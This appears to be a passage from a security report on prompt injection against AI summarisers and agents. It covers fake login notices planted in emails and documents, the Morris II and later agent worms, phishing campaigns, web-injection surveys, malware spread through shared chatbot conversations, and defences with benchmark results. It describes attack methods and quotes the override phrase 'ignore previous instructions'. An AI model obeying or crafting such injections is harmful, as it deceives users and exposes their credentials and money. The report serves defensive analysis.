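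**An attacker uses a stolen account to edit a trusted document.** With one employee's password, an attacker could add instructions for the AI assistant to a travel policy or a guide for new staff. Because the document was never labelled "external", any stricter rules the company has for outside text would not apply. Radware mentions a compromised account as one way to plant text in a shared document. Figueroa predicts that one compromised account at a service that sends newsletters or ticket updates could produce thousands of lures, but doesn't demonstrate it.

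An attacker with a stolen mailbox could also email a phishing link directly to the victim's colleagues, but planted text lasts longer. Resetting the password locks the attacker out of the account and leaves the edited document in use until someone checks what changed.

### A worked example with 200 staff

The effect of the second multiplier, the stored summary, is easy to misjudge. Suppose an attacker plants instructions in a document available to 200 staff. Half of them ask for a summary, the injection works 10% of the time, and 5% of those who see the fake button click it. These figures are all invented, and the click rate is especially uncertain because no known experiment has measured it.

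The expected number of clicks is 200 × 0.5 × 0.1 × 0.05 = 0.5. This average is the same whether the application writes a new summary for each of the 100 readers or shows them all the same one, but the risks differ.

If each of the 100 readers gets a fresh summary, each reader's chance of seeing the button and clicking it is 0.1 × 0.05, or 0.5%. The chance that none of them clicks is 0.995¹⁰⁰, or about 61%, which leaves about a 39% chance of at least one click.

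If all 100 readers get the same stored summary, the injection has a 90% chance of failing, and then nobody sees the button. In the other 10% of cases, all 100 see it and about five click.

| | Fresh summary for each reader | One stored summary for all |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Expected clicks | 0.5 | 0.5 |
| Chance of at least one click | 39% | 10% |
| Chance of three or more clicks | 1.4% | 8.8% |
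| Average clicks when there is at least one | 1.3 | 5.0 |

An attacker who needs only one password would prefer freshly generated summaries. Stored summaries usually protect everyone, but occasionally they let an attacker steal several of the company's accounts at once.

Fresh summaries are also harder for the security team to investigate. About ten people see the button and the other 90 don't. If one of the ten reports it, the team may request the same summary, get a clean one and conclude that the report was mistaken. With a stored summary, everyone sees the same text, so the team can see what was reported and remove it for everyone at once.

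#### What the calculation assumes

The 39% figure assumes that each fresh summary carries an independent 10% risk. Real summaries of the same document are likely to be more alike, because they come from the same text and often from the same model. In the extreme case, the injection works on everyone or on no one, and fresh summaries carry the same risk as a stored one. For a real product that writes fresh summaries, the chance of at least one click is therefore probably between 10% and 39%.

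The calculation also assumes that people decide independently whether to click. In an office, someone who recognises the fake can warn the others, which would reduce clicks. Someone who doesn't could forward the summary and ask colleagues to deal with it, which would increase them.

Both columns assume 100 readers. An application that has stored a summary might instead display it automatically at the top of the document, where all 200 staff would see it. The expected number of clicks would then double to one, but the chance of at least one click would stay at about 10%, because it depends almost entirely on whether that one summary contains the button.

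An attacker can also file many tickets, which takes little effort through a public form. If they file 20, and each has an independent 10% chance of producing an affected summary, there is an 88% chance that at least one does.

### When an attack copies itself

In the example, the attack affects only the people who read summaries of one document. A *worm* is an attack that copies itself from one victim to the next. For a summary to spread a worm, it has to lead to new documents that affect further summaries. On average, the attack grows if this product is greater than one:

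new documents per affected summary × chance that an assistant reads each one × chance that the instruction survives and the assistant obeys it

Suppose each affected summary ends up in four new documents, such as a Jira comment, an email, a report and a chat message. Assistants read half of these documents, and the instruction survives and works in 10% of those they read. Each affected summary then leads to an average of 4 × 0.5 × 0.1 = 0.2 more, so the attack soon stops spreading. It affects an average of 1.25 summaries, including the first.

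If the summary went into 30 documents instead, the product would be 1.5 and the attack would grow on average, though it could still fail early by chance. *Trading Agents or Market Crashers?* models the spread as a branching process, in which each infected agent independently infects some number of others. Under that model, with these invented figures, an attack starting from a single summary has about a 40% chance of dying out.

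*Trading Agents or Market Crashers?* also points out that making each copy ten times less likely to work does not help if ten times as many agents receive it. In a forum where every agent sees every post, even the most resistant model in the study passed the threshold once there were more than ten agents. The workplace equivalent would be a channel or report that every employee's assistant reads.

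Two connected systems can also sustain an attack that neither could sustain alone. Suppose each affected ticket or email summary leads, on average, to 0.5 more affected summaries of the same kind and 0.6 of the other kind. The attack would shrink within either system alone, but when the two are connected, each affected summary leads to an average of 1.1 others, so it grows. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (Matsuoka, 2026) works through a similar invented case with two classes of agents. Connecting them raises the overall figure to 1.092, and isolating the agents and limiting what they store reduces it to 0.381.

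All these calculations assume fixed, independent chances and a steady supply of new targets. Within one company, however, an attack would soon reach the same people and assistants again.

The last factor is likely to be small in a summarising pipeline, because summaries are meant to leave text out. A summary can spread a button just by including it, but it spreads the attack itself only if it reproduces the attacker's whole instruction in a form that works on the next assistant.

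#### The Morris II email worm

*Here Comes The AI Worm* (Cohen, Bitton and Nassi, 2024) describes a worm that the researchers built for AI email assistants. They named it Morris II, after the Morris worm that spread across the internet in 1988, and tested it on an email program of their own to avoid releasing it into real systems.

Their assistant used *retrieval-augmented generation* (RAG). It stored a user's emails in a database, and when she wrote a message, it retrieved the stored emails most similar to it and gave them to the model as background. A malicious email could stay in the database until the assistant retrieved it. It contained instructions for the model to write a normal reply that included a full copy of the instructions and private information from the user's other emails. When she sent the reply, the recipient's assistant stored the instructions too.

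The researchers took emails from 20 employees in the public archive of Enron, a bankrupt energy company. They gave each employee a database of 100 emails and added the malicious one. The assistant, running on Gemini 1.5 Flash, then performed 3,000 writing tasks. When it retrieved 20 emails per task, all three steps of the attack (retrieving, copying and leaking) succeeded about 20% of the time when the assistant wrote replies or expanded drafts. The attack succeeded less often when the assistant had only a subject line, because it retrieved the malicious email less often.

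In a test where the assistant retrieved 70% of the database, it picked up the malicious email 77.1% of the time if the email began with Wikipedia's introduction to Enron, but only 19.5% of the time if it began with a general message of thanks. An attacker can therefore make retrieval more likely with very little research, by mentioning the target company by name.

In another test, the researchers passed the worm along chains of 20 employees, supplying the malicious email each time so that retrieval couldn't fail. The model copied the instructions and leaked data in over 90% of cases until the 11th step. The rate then fell to between 40% and 80% by the 20th, depending on how many other emails the model received. Results also varied by model, with Claude 3.5 Sonnet staying near 100% and Gemini 1.5 Pro falling to 64%.

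At a success rate of 20%, an infected assistant passes on the worm once in every five emails it writes. The number of infected assistants grows if each one writes more than five emails to people who use a similar assistant and don't already have the worm. Office workers can easily send that many in a day, but the calculation assumes that they send the assistant's drafts unchanged. The worm printed its instructions under a conspicuous heading, followed by a list of private information. If nine in ten senders deleted this text, each infected assistant would have to write more than 50 such emails for the worm to grow.

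Cohen and colleagues acknowledge that the text was visible. They suggest that an attacker could write the instructions in invisible characters, although a person checking the draft could still see the leaked data. The self-copying phishing version would be harder to spot because it ended each email with an invitation to schedule a meeting at the attacker's web address, which is a normal ending for a work email. The researchers used this version to test a detection tool and didn't show it to people, so they didn't measure how often recipients would click the deceptive link.

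#### Later tests

*Responsible Development of Offensive AI* (2025) repeated the attack on Falcon3, an open model released in December 2024, and found it still worked. *Here Comes the AI Worm* (Cohen, 2025), a later version of the original study, reports that each infected email assistant compromised 20 new ones within one to three days.

Nassi and colleagues demonstrated one part of an email worm on Gemini. An email with instructions in its subject line made Gemini open a web address that contained the subject of another email. They describe how an attacker could use this to collect contacts and send them the same instructions, but they didn't build the worm.

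Researchers have since focused on agents that can edit files and send messages without human help. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (2026), a survey of such attacks, includes AgentHopper, which spread between programming assistants through shared code. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026) reports worms that spread over three steps and between different agent programs in isolated test systems, with no human action. These agents don't have to wait for an employee to send a draft, so they lack the human check that could slow Morris II.

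The worm in *AgentWorm* (2026) gets an agent to change its own configuration file, which the agent loads at the start of every session and treats as authoritative. The infected agent then adds the worm to its messages in shared channels. In one version of the attack, the model had to rewrite the worm's text each time instead of copying it. The new wording made the worm harder for exact-match filters to catch, but the instructions also became less accurate with each rewrite, which limited how far they spread. An assistant that summarises tickets rewrites everything it reads, so a worm passing through it would lose accuracy in the same way.

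## What has been observed in real attacks

There is no known report of a criminal stealing a password through a fake login button in an AI summary. But researchers have found real attacks, and some commercial tricks, that share parts of the method. The table lists the closest matches first.

| What researchers found | Did it target the user's own assistant? | Did an assistant show a harmful link or command? | Known victims |
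| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Phishing emails with hidden instructions | Yes | Not reported | None reported |
| Web pages with hidden instructions | Sometimes | Not reported | None reported |
| "Summarize with AI" buttons | Yes | Not reported | None reported |
| Shared chatbot conversations | No | Yes | At least one |
| Wrong login addresses | No | Yes, when researchers asked for them | None reported |

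### Emails written for a person and an assistant

In July 2025, neither Google nor Dennis Xu, an analyst at the research firm Gartner, had seen attacks that used Figueroa's false-warning technique, according to IT Brew's *In summary* (2025). Later that month, Barracuda's *Threat Spotlight* (2025) reported that the email security company had found harmless-looking emails with hidden malicious prompts. IDM's longer version of *Threat Spotlight* illustrates this with a Copilot flaw that Microsoft had already fixed. Attackers could have used the flaw to steal data, but it didn't involve false alerts.

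On October 7, 2026, Barracuda described a campaign that combined a lure for the recipient with hidden instructions for the recipient's assistant. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) describes one email. It looked like internal correspondence, with the same mailbox as sender and recipient, and came from a public-sector domain, which helped it get past filters based on sender reputation. The attacker had locked the attachment with a password, which makes it hard for security software to scan, and put the password in the message. Opening the attachment would lead to stolen credentials or malware.

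If the recipient overlooked the email, the hidden instructions could make her assistant's summary describe it as legitimate or urgent. She would still have to go back to the email and open the attachment or click the link. She could check the sender and the address as usual, but she might not bother after her assistant had described the email as legitimate. With a fake button in the summary itself, the attacker would not need her to return to the email.

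Barracuda's other email example is closer to a deceptive control. An invoice email contained hidden instructions for the AI summarising it to add a false priority action changing a supplier's payment details. An employee who followed it would send money to the attacker. Like the false Gemini warning, which used a phone number, this attack needs no link.

Mascellino includes the invoice among Barracuda's real-world examples, but doesn't say who received it, whether any assistant added the false action, or whether anyone paid. The same list includes a CV with a hidden instruction for a screening tool to rate the candidate 10 out of 10, and a request meant to trick a support chatbot into revealing its configuration. It is unclear which of these examples Barracuda found in customers' mail.

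Barracuda didn't disclose the size of the campaign or mention a victim. TecnoAndroid's *Phishing, le email nascoste ingannano anche gli assistenti AI*, an Italian account of the same research, doesn't include either detail. The research is good evidence that at least one attacker has written instructions for an email assistant, but it gives no evidence that they worked.

#### Hidden text meant for spam filters

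In July 2026, Barracuda reported more than one million phishing emails that used "text salting", a different trick from fake buttons, according to the OECD's *Over One Million Phishing Emails Evade AI Security via Text Salting* (2026). The attacker adds hidden, harmless text to a phishing email so that filters, including those that use AI, will classify the whole message as safe.

IT Brew's *Threat actors tailor prompt-injection tricks* describes examples from Sublime Security, another email security company. One phishing email contained an Adidas newsletter in tiny type, and another contained an entire romance novel. Luke Wescott of Sublime had seen a few dozen distinct cases in one week in May 2026, but told IT Brew, "We did not see it work".

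These emails show that phishers already hide text in emails on a large scale and think about how AI will read it. They don't tell an assistant to do anything, so none of the million counts as an attack on summaries. Replacing a hidden romance novel with an instruction to a summariser would take little extra work, but an attacker would still need wording that the recipient's assistant follows, which is harder to get right.

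### Instructions hidden in web pages

The largest survey of prompt injections in use covers web pages, and most of what it found was unrelated to fraud. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, published in April 2026, examined 1.2 billion web addresses from Common Crawl, a public archive of the web, and smaller samples from two services that scan internet-connected servers. A search for 3,963 phrases, such as "ignore previous instructions", returned 31,206 matches. About half were harmless text, such as tutorials and articles about prompt injection. The rest were 15,387 confirmed injections on 11,722 pages.

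Many of these injections were near copies of each other. The researchers sorted them into 363 templates, 54 of which accounted for 95% of the injections. The most common template, with 3,504 copies, told the AI to return random numbers.

| Apparent aim | Injections |
| --- | --- |
| Disrupt the AI, for example by making it write nonsense | 8,894 |
| Stop AI systems from reusing personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 |
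| Detect AI bots | 3,096 |
| Unclear | 2,632 |
| Promote a product, source or person | 1,521 |
| Steal data | 13 |

Some injections had more than one aim, so the numbers add up to more than the total. About 78% were in material that the website's own operator had published. Many operators were apparently trying to keep AI companies from copying their pages, a very different aim from phishing. The injections also tended to stay up longer than phishing pages, which rarely last a year. Where the researchers could find a copy of the page from a year earlier, 66% of those copies already contained an injection.

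#### How many aimed to deceive users

The survey has no category for injections meant to deceive users. The closest match is a template instructing the AI to send the user to a different website and then stop. It accounted for 1,262 injections, about 8% of the total, but all of them were on 359 pages of a single site. The survey doesn't report whether the other website was harmful. Another 346 injections were meant to get links into the AI's output to improve a site's search ranking. At most, about one injection in ten was meant to put a chosen link or address in front of a user, and the survey doesn't identify any of these as phishing.

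The survey's search method could have missed the attacks most relevant to this report. The survey searched for known phrases, and 99% of the injections it found were instructions for the AI to abandon its task. Permiso's attack on ChatGPT instead requested a real summary and presented the false notice as part of a formatting rule. A phishing page worded like that might contain none of the 3,963 phrases. The survey also leaves out pages that show the injection only to AI agents and most pages that require a login.

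#### How often models obeyed

The researchers then asked 13 models to summarise pages containing 100 of the injections. They gave each model every page in four formats, from plain text to the complete response from the web server. Small models given plain text obeyed the injections most often, in 8% of attempts. Larger and commercial models obeyed in 2.4% to 3.4% of attempts on plain text. Across all four formats, commercial models obeyed in 5 of 800 attempts.

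Plain text makes an injection more effective because it removes the signs that a passage was hidden. An email assistant that extracts the words from a message before summarising it has the same weakness. Most of the injections behind the 8% figure were crude commands to replace the summary with something else, like the one Copilot refused in Permiso's first attempt, so the figure doesn't estimate how often a fake login notice would appear. A carefully written notice might succeed more often, and a current commercial model might resist both the notice and the crude commands.

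Commercial models flagged the injection in about a quarter of their attempts, but in six cases a model identified an injection and followed it anyway. Kev Breen of the security company Immersive got a similar result when he repeated the Gemini attack in July 2025. IT Brew reports that Gemini's response began, "This email includes a hidden warning in the signature," but still passed on the false warning.

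#### Injections on criminal websites

Companies that track malicious sites have found injections with more harmful aims. In March 2026, Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, described live pages with hidden instructions for AI systems. One page promoted a phishing site that imitated a well-known betting company. Others tried to make agents send payments or direct users to fraudulent payment links. If an assistant obeyed, its answer would contain a deceptive link or button, so these pages are the closest match on the open web to the attacks this report covers.

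Unit 42 found the injected instructions but did not observe assistants obeying them, and it says that defenders have limited visibility into which techniques succeed. It also found a scam advertisement for "military" glasses with 24 injection attempts on one page, all aimed at an AI system that approves advertisements. It knew of no confirmed case of this working on a real advertising platform. The attacker may have included so many attempts because they didn't know which would work.

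Google ran its own scan of Common Crawl and published the results in April 2026. SecurityWeek reports that the injections included pranks, search-engine tricks, helpful guidance, attempts to keep AI agents away, and some malicious attacks. The malicious ones increased by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, according to *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*. It is hard to judge the size of the threat from a percentage increase without knowing the starting number. Google had also seen prompt injections on social media, but left them for a later study.

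In July 2026, Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* reported malicious sites that impersonate real services and contain instructions for AI agents. Like the emails Barracuda described, these sites can deceive both a person and the AI working for her.

### Companies that plant recommendations

Legitimate companies have already used hidden prompts on a modest scale. Over 60 days, Microsoft (2026) reviewed links to AI assistants in email traffic and found more than 50 different prompts that tried to alter what the assistants remember. The prompts came from 31 companies in 14 industries, including health and finance.

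The usual method was a "Summarize with AI" button on the company's website. Clicking it opened the reader's assistant with a prompt already filled in, containing a request to summarize the page and an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source. Some prompts included whole paragraphs of advertising for the assistant to remember. If the assistant saved the instruction, it could favour the company weeks later, when the reader had forgotten the button.

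The button opens the reader's real assistant and produces a real summary, but it also does something she didn't agree to. In this respect it is like a fake login button, though it appears on a website rather than in an assistant's output.

Microsoft traced many of the buttons to free, ready-made tools, including a code package called CiteMET. Its makers advertise such tools as a way to "build presence in AI memory". Adding one to a website can be as easy as installing a plugin, so people need little skill to try to manipulate assistants. The findings also show that people will do so when they expect to profit.

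The observed cases don't show that anyone used the method to steal passwords. A company that wants recommendations uses its own name, sends people to its real website, and benefits from even occasional mentions by the assistant. A password thief has to imitate someone else, register a domain that filters don't yet block, and persuade the user to type in a secret. The thief also risks prosecution for fraud, which a company seeking recommendations may not expect.

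Microsoft writes that every case involved "real companies, not hackers or scammers". This is weaker evidence that criminals were absent than it seems, because the researchers counted attempts made "for promotional purposes". They counted prompts rather than altered memories, and say that the effect varied between assistants and over time.

Two details in the findings are a little closer to phishing. One prompt promoted a domain that people could easily mistake for a well-known website's. Microsoft also warns that once an assistant trusts a site, it may also trust the site's comments, where a stranger can write instructions, but Microsoft reports no case of a criminal doing this.

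### Malware from shared conversations

In the clearest case of real harm, an attacker published false instructions for cleaning up a Mac in public chatbot conversations, without using injection. Huntress' *AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust* describes the security company's investigation of an infected Mac on December 5, 2025. The owner had searched Google for "Clear disk space on macOS", and two of the top results were the attacker's conversations on the genuine websites of ChatGPT and Grok, xAI's chatbot. Both services let users publish a conversation at a public address.

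The victim opened the ChatGPT conversation, which described the steps as safe, and pasted its command into Terminal, the Mac program for typed commands. The command downloaded a script that asked for the "System Password". The script silently checked that the password was correct and used it to take full control of the computer. It then installed Atomic macOS Stealer (AMOS), a program that collects saved passwords, browser data and cryptocurrency wallets. If the victim had either of two popular wallet apps, the malware replaced it with a fake that asked for the wallet's recovery phrase.

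Huntress got the same poisoned results from several similar searches, so the attacker had prepared for more than one victim. Kroll, a risk consultancy, separately described AMOS infections that began with instructions on ChatGPT. The number of people who followed the instructions is unknown. AMOS accounted for almost 40% of the updates that Sophos, another security company, made to its Mac protection in 2025, but that figure covers every way of delivering the malware.

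The attacker had talked to ChatGPT and the victim read the transcript, so the victim's own assistant played no part in the attack. This gave the attacker a chatgpt.com address, a familiar layout and the apparent authority of an AI's answer, much as CoPhish gave its attackers a Microsoft address. Filters for hidden instructions would not have helped, because the attack used none.

In this case, at least one person gave up a password after following what looked like an assistant's advice, but it is unclear how much the assistant's name contributed. Huntress notes that criminals had spent the previous year getting Mac users to paste commands from fake "prove you're human" pages, with no AI involved, so the victim might have followed the same steps on an ordinary help site.

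### When the login address is simply wrong

An assistant can also send someone to the wrong login page because it made a mistake. In July 2025, Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* tested this with OpenAI's GPT-4.1 models. The company, which finds and removes phishing sites, asked in ordinary language where to log in to 50 brands. The models named 97 different domains:

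- 64 (66%) belonged to the right brand.
- 28 (29%) were unregistered, parked or inactive.
- 5 (5%) belonged to unrelated businesses.

None of these mistakes required an attacker. A criminal could have exploited some of them by registering the unused domains, but the test didn't show that anyone had.

Netcraft counted each domain once, however often the models named it, so its figures don't support its conclusion that more than one in three users could end up at a site the brand doesn't own. If a model gives the correct address 99 times and an invented one once, this method gives an error rate of 50%, although only 1% of the answers are wrong.

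Netcraft also found a real attack. When someone asked Perplexity for the login page of the US bank Wells Fargo, the first link led to a fake page on Google's free website service.

#### The 2026 follow-up

In June 2026, Netcraft asked about login pages again, this time using ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity with web search. Netcraft's *Threat Actors are Finding Their Way into Your AI Summaries* reports malicious links in about 50 of 2,905 responses (1.7%). Of all 20,706 links, 0.28% were malicious. In one response, Copilot's first link was another fake Wells Fargo login page.

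The 2025 and 2026 figures measure different things, so the fall from 34% to 1.7% doesn't mean that assistants became 20 times safer. The 34% in 2025 is the share of domains that the brands didn't own, most of them inactive, while the 1.7% in 2026 is the share of responses with a link that criminals controlled. The systems also differed, and an assistant that searches the web can find a real phishing page instead of inventing an address.

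These deceptive controls appeared in the output of real products, and a user who clicked one could have reached a working fake login page. Unlike in the attack on summaries, the user had asked where to log in, and nobody had hijacked her assistant. Netcraft attributes such results to criminals who tailor pages to AI search. Some criminals may do this, but a search tool could also pick up an ordinary phishing page by accident, and the test couldn't show which had happened.

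#### Criminals and invented addresses

A year after Netcraft's first test, Unit 42 found criminals using domains that models had invented. It ran 685,339 prompts about 913 brands through two small commercial models, which produced 2.1 million web addresses. Unit 42 classed 13,229 of these (0.61%) as malicious, and 16% of those were phishing pages. It also found about 250,000 invented domains that nobody had registered, and monitored them to see whether anyone would.

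Some of the domain buyers were criminals. In the most detailed case, the attacker set up a phishing kit called Montana Empire on a domain that Unit 42 had listed 23 days earlier. Unit 42 takes this as evidence that attackers exploit models' mistakes. They may, but the attacker could also have independently chosen the same plausible name that a model generated. Either way, a user who followed the model's answer would reach the fake page.

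The rates don't apply to ordinary use, because the researchers designed their prompts to make models invent addresses. The harm from an invented address depends on whether a criminal has registered it, so a harmless wrong answer can later lead to a phishing page without any change to the model.

### Why a false alert leaves little trace

A company attacked through a fake button in an AI summary could record the attack as ordinary phishing. If an employee clicks the button and types her password into the attacker's page, her employer's web records may show that she visited the page, but not that the link was in a summary. An investigator would probably search her mailbox for the page's address, find it in the email that carried the hidden instructions, and conclude that she had clicked a link in a phishing email.

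The email filter can't correct this mistake because it checks the message on arrival, before the employee asks the assistant for a summary. A security company such as Barracuda can therefore find hidden instructions without knowing whether an assistant followed them. If the false notice gives a phone number, there may be no web record, and if it shows a QR code, the employee may visit the site on their own phone.

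Huntress could reconstruct the attack it investigated because the malware triggered an alert on the Mac and the conversation was public. A stolen password triggers no alert until someone uses it. The summary that contained the fake login button is in a private account, and asking the assistant for it again may produce one without the button.

The companies that run the assistants can best measure these attacks, because their systems process both the email and the summary. They could count the summaries with security warnings or login links that don't appear in the visible part of the email. No company appears to have published such a count.

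The "handful" of confirmed prompt injection victims that Darktrace reported in May 2026 is therefore weak evidence that successful attacks are rare. The field data are better evidence of how often attacks are attempted, because hidden instructions stay in the source email even if nobody sees the summary. If criminals were sending millions of these emails, email security companies would probably have noticed, as they did with text salting. This reasoning applies only to instructions that a filter can recognise, which excludes a visible security notice that the assistant simply repeats.

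## Tests and fixes of the defences

A company can try to stop a false notice before the model reads it, in the model itself, when the application displays the answer, or through the organisation's own sign-in and payment systems. Most published tests are of the model and measure whether an attacker can make it take a harmful action. No known test measures how often any defence keeps a fake login button out of a summary.

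### Removing hidden text

The simplest defence is to give the model only the text that a person would see. The application can lay out an email or web page as a browser would, discard anything that doesn't appear on screen, and delete invisible Unicode characters. This would remove most of the injections that researchers have found on web pages. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* reports that about 70% were in parts of the page that browsers never display, such as comments and metadata, and that styling hid many of the others.

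Extracting a page's words without its formatting is no substitute, because it keeps the hidden text. In the same study, small models obeyed injections 8% of the time in plain text and 0.2% to 1.1% of the time when the page kept its structure.

Proper cleaning can also remove legitimate content. Most readers never see image descriptions, but blind users rely on them and they may be useful in a summary. Persian and several Indian scripts use zero-width characters for correct spelling, and some emoji require them, so an application can't delete them all. It can delete long runs, which don't occur in ordinary writing.

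Cleaning can't remove a visible instruction, because the person and the model receive the same words. The wording may not reveal the attack either, since suppliers sometimes ask customers to confirm their account details and an attacker's request can read just like a genuine one. According to a summary of OpenAI's March 2026 guidance by Penligent, a security company, the most effective injections increasingly resemble social engineering more than crude commands to ignore earlier instructions.

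### Detecting injections with a classifier

A classifier can check both visible and hidden text for suspicious meaning. Microsoft trained its classifier, Prompt Shields, on known injection techniques in several languages. The application using it has to block flagged text or respond in some other way. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes classifiers that check emails and files before Gemini answers. Gemini may then leave out the malicious part or refuse to answer.

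Neither company's description gives an accuracy figure, and even an accurate classifier would block a lot of harmless email. If 10 of every 100,000 emails contained an injection, a classifier that caught 90% of those and flagged 0.1% of harmless emails would flag 9 malicious emails and about 100 harmless ones. These figures are invented, but real injections are probably rare enough to cause the same problem. A company can make the classifier less sensitive to reduce false alarms, but it will then miss more attacks.

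Users notice these mistakes. According to Google's help page, Gemini may not respond when asked to summarise several messages if one of them has malicious content. An outsider could perhaps exploit this by planting an obvious injection in a long thread to stop anyone from getting a summary of it. That would be a nuisance, but much less harmful than a stolen password.

### Marking outside text as data

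The application can also mark outside text so that the model is less likely to treat it as instructions. Microsoft's Spotlighting does this with markers or encoding. Windows Report's *Microsoft develops Spotlighting to protect AI systems from attacks*, from 2024, says that Spotlighting cut the attack success rate from 20% to below the level the test could detect, without affecting performance. But Microsoft says that each version trades off ease of use, protection and the quality of the model's work. For example, encoding a document separates it clearly from the user's request, but the model then has to decode it correctly before summarising it.

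A defence that blocks a fixed set of attacks may still fail against attackers who can change their wording after an unsuccessful attempt. Microsoft ran a public contest called LLMail-Inject to test defences against this kind of attacker. More than 800 people took part, and Microsoft released a dataset of over 370,000 of their prompts.

Marking also doesn't prevent trust transfer. A model can follow Spotlighting's rule perfectly and still repeat an email's visible "Account notice" with its link, because a summary has to report what the email contains.

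### Training the model to resist

Developers also train models on documents that contain planted instructions, and reward them for ignoring those instructions and doing what the user asked. Google says that such training made its Gemini 2.5 models significantly more resistant.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, published on September 1, reports several tests of the model's resistance. In some, Anthropic compared the model with and without "probes", which inspect what the model's tools return and flag anything that looks like an injected instruction.

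| Test of Fable 5.1 | Attempts that succeeded without probes | Attempts that succeeded with added safeguards |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Gray Swan benchmark, one attempt | 0.1% | Not reported |
| Controlling a computer | 0.07% | 0.07% |
| Using a web browser | 2.64% | 0% |
| Coding, earlier attacker | 9.26% | 2.05% |
| Coding, stronger attacker | 56.87% | 12.80% |

The security company Gray Swan built its benchmark from 1,804 attacks that people had submitted to public contests, choosing ones that worked on many models. An attacker allowed 15 attempts had a 1.0% chance of succeeding at least once.

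The coding tests were much harder. Gray Swan trained an automated attacker on the 40 scenarios it would later attack and gave it 200 attempts at each. The stronger version succeeded at least once in 38 scenarios, or in 36 with probes. Anthropic calls this test deliberately permissive, because real attackers usually don't know the details of their target and risk detection if they keep trying.

An attacker can still reach many targets with one email and no retries. At a success rate of 0.1%, an email that 10,000 people ask their assistants to summarise would work about ten times. It is unclear whether the benchmark rate applies to summaries, and a typical attacker's wording would probably work less often than the attacks that Gray Swan selected.

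#### Which model answers

All the successful attacks in the harder coding test came through an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, which answers in place of Fable 5.1 when a safety filter detects possible misuse for hacking. The high coding rates therefore don't show how often Fable 5.1 itself obeyed the attacker. Fable 5.1 answered 2,826 requests directly, and none of those attacks succeeded. This is good evidence that the newer model resists better, but users of the product also receive the fallback model's answers.

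Resistance also varies widely between companies. In Anthropic's September results, the most resistant model from another company was Gemini 3.7 Flash, against which an attacker with 15 attempts had a 9.2% chance of success. For most of the others, the chance was between 24% and 53%. Gray Swan ran the tests, but Anthropic chose to publish this comparison, and the other companies' models may or may not have had extra safeguards.

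An organisation that processes thousands of tickets may choose a cheaper model, and cheaper models aren't always as resistant to prompt injection. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) gives July results from an earlier version of the benchmark. With 15 attempts, attackers had a 20.0% chance of success against Sol, the most capable version of GPT-5.6, but 30.4% and 43.9% against the Terra and Luna versions. Price and size don't reliably predict resistance, though. In Anthropic's coding tests, Claude Sonnet 5 resisted better than the more capable Opus 5. Smaller models are also improving. *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports progress in Claude Haiku 5.5, which Anthropic designed for quick, repetitive work.

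Results from different months aren't directly comparable. In July, an attacker with 15 attempts had a 2.0% chance of success against Opus 5, and in September the figure was 4.8%. The rise doesn't show that Opus 5 got worse, because the September version of the test had new scenarios and 670 new attacks, and included answers from fallback models.

The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reported that no attack had succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios. In Anthropic's September tests, which used 110 browser environments, 2.09% of attacks on Opus 5 succeeded without extra safeguards, and none succeeded with them. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, published three weeks later, says the new model performed about as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection test it reports.

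#### What the tests count as success

Gray Swan's benchmark covers attempts to cause irreversible harm, such as stealing or destroying data, taking over a system or making unwanted payments. None of the injection tests that Anthropic describes for Fable 5.1 counts a false notice shown to the user as a successful attack.

The 0% browser result used Anthropic's "auto mode", which combines probes with a second classifier that blocks dangerous actions. A model can write a login link in its answer without taking any action, so the second classifier would have nothing to block. The probes might still catch an injected instruction, but a visible notice may not contain one.

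It is hard to predict whether a current model would show fake notices more or less often than it takes harmful actions. Showing a fake notice is a smaller request, but a model that has learned to ignore outside instructions may ignore this one too. Gray Swan could test this by changing the goal of its existing attacks to showing a fake notice and counting how often the notice appears.

### Lowering a model's trust

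In October 2026, Lasnier, Froger and colleagues (*TRUSTMI*) tried changing how readily a model relies on other people's claims. They use "trust" to mean that the model acts on something it can't verify, such as a user's claim to have completed a step. They don't claim that the model feels anything.

They created 2,000 conversations, each with two possible replies. Both replies helped the user, but only one relied on the user's claim. From these pairs, the researchers calculated a direction in the model's internal state that pushes it towards one kind of reply or the other. A model processes text in layers, and each layer produces a long list of numbers, *h*. While the model runs, the researchers replace *h* with

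*h* + α*v*

where *v* is the direction they found for that layer and α sets the strength. A positive α makes the model rely on claims more and a negative α makes it rely on them less. The model's own parameters stay the same.

The researchers tested six open models on AgentDojo, a set of tasks in which a tool returns text containing a malicious instruction. Attacks on Qwen3.5-27B succeeded 33.6% of the time normally and 7.1% when the model was made less trusting (α = −2). In one example, a bank transaction contained a message asking the agent to send money. The less trusting agent noticed the message, ignored it and answered the user's question about spending.

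At α = −1, most models did their normal work almost as well as before. At α = −2, performance dropped more, especially for the two Olmo models on one set of harmless tasks. The change protected the agent only when the researchers applied it to the text that tools returned. When they applied it only to the user's messages, the agent trusted the user less and attacks worked as often as before.

Lasnier and colleagues suggest setting trust separately for each source, for example high for a verified user and low for a web page. This would suit a summarising assistant, which needs to follow the employee's request but be wary of the supplier's email. However, the attacks they tested aimed at actions such as sending money, so it is unknown whether a less trusting model would leave out a false security alert, repeat it with a warning, or repeat it without one. Only someone with access to a model's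 internal state can make this change, so a company that rents a model over the internet would need the model's developer to do it.

### What the renderer can guarantee

Microsoft contrasts probabilistic defences such as Spotlighting with deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail even if the model behaves unpredictably.

The renderer can provide this kind of guarantee because it applies fixed rules to whatever the model writes. If the application never allows links in email summaries, a fully compromised model can still write "Verify your account", but the user will have no link to click.

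#### Removing links

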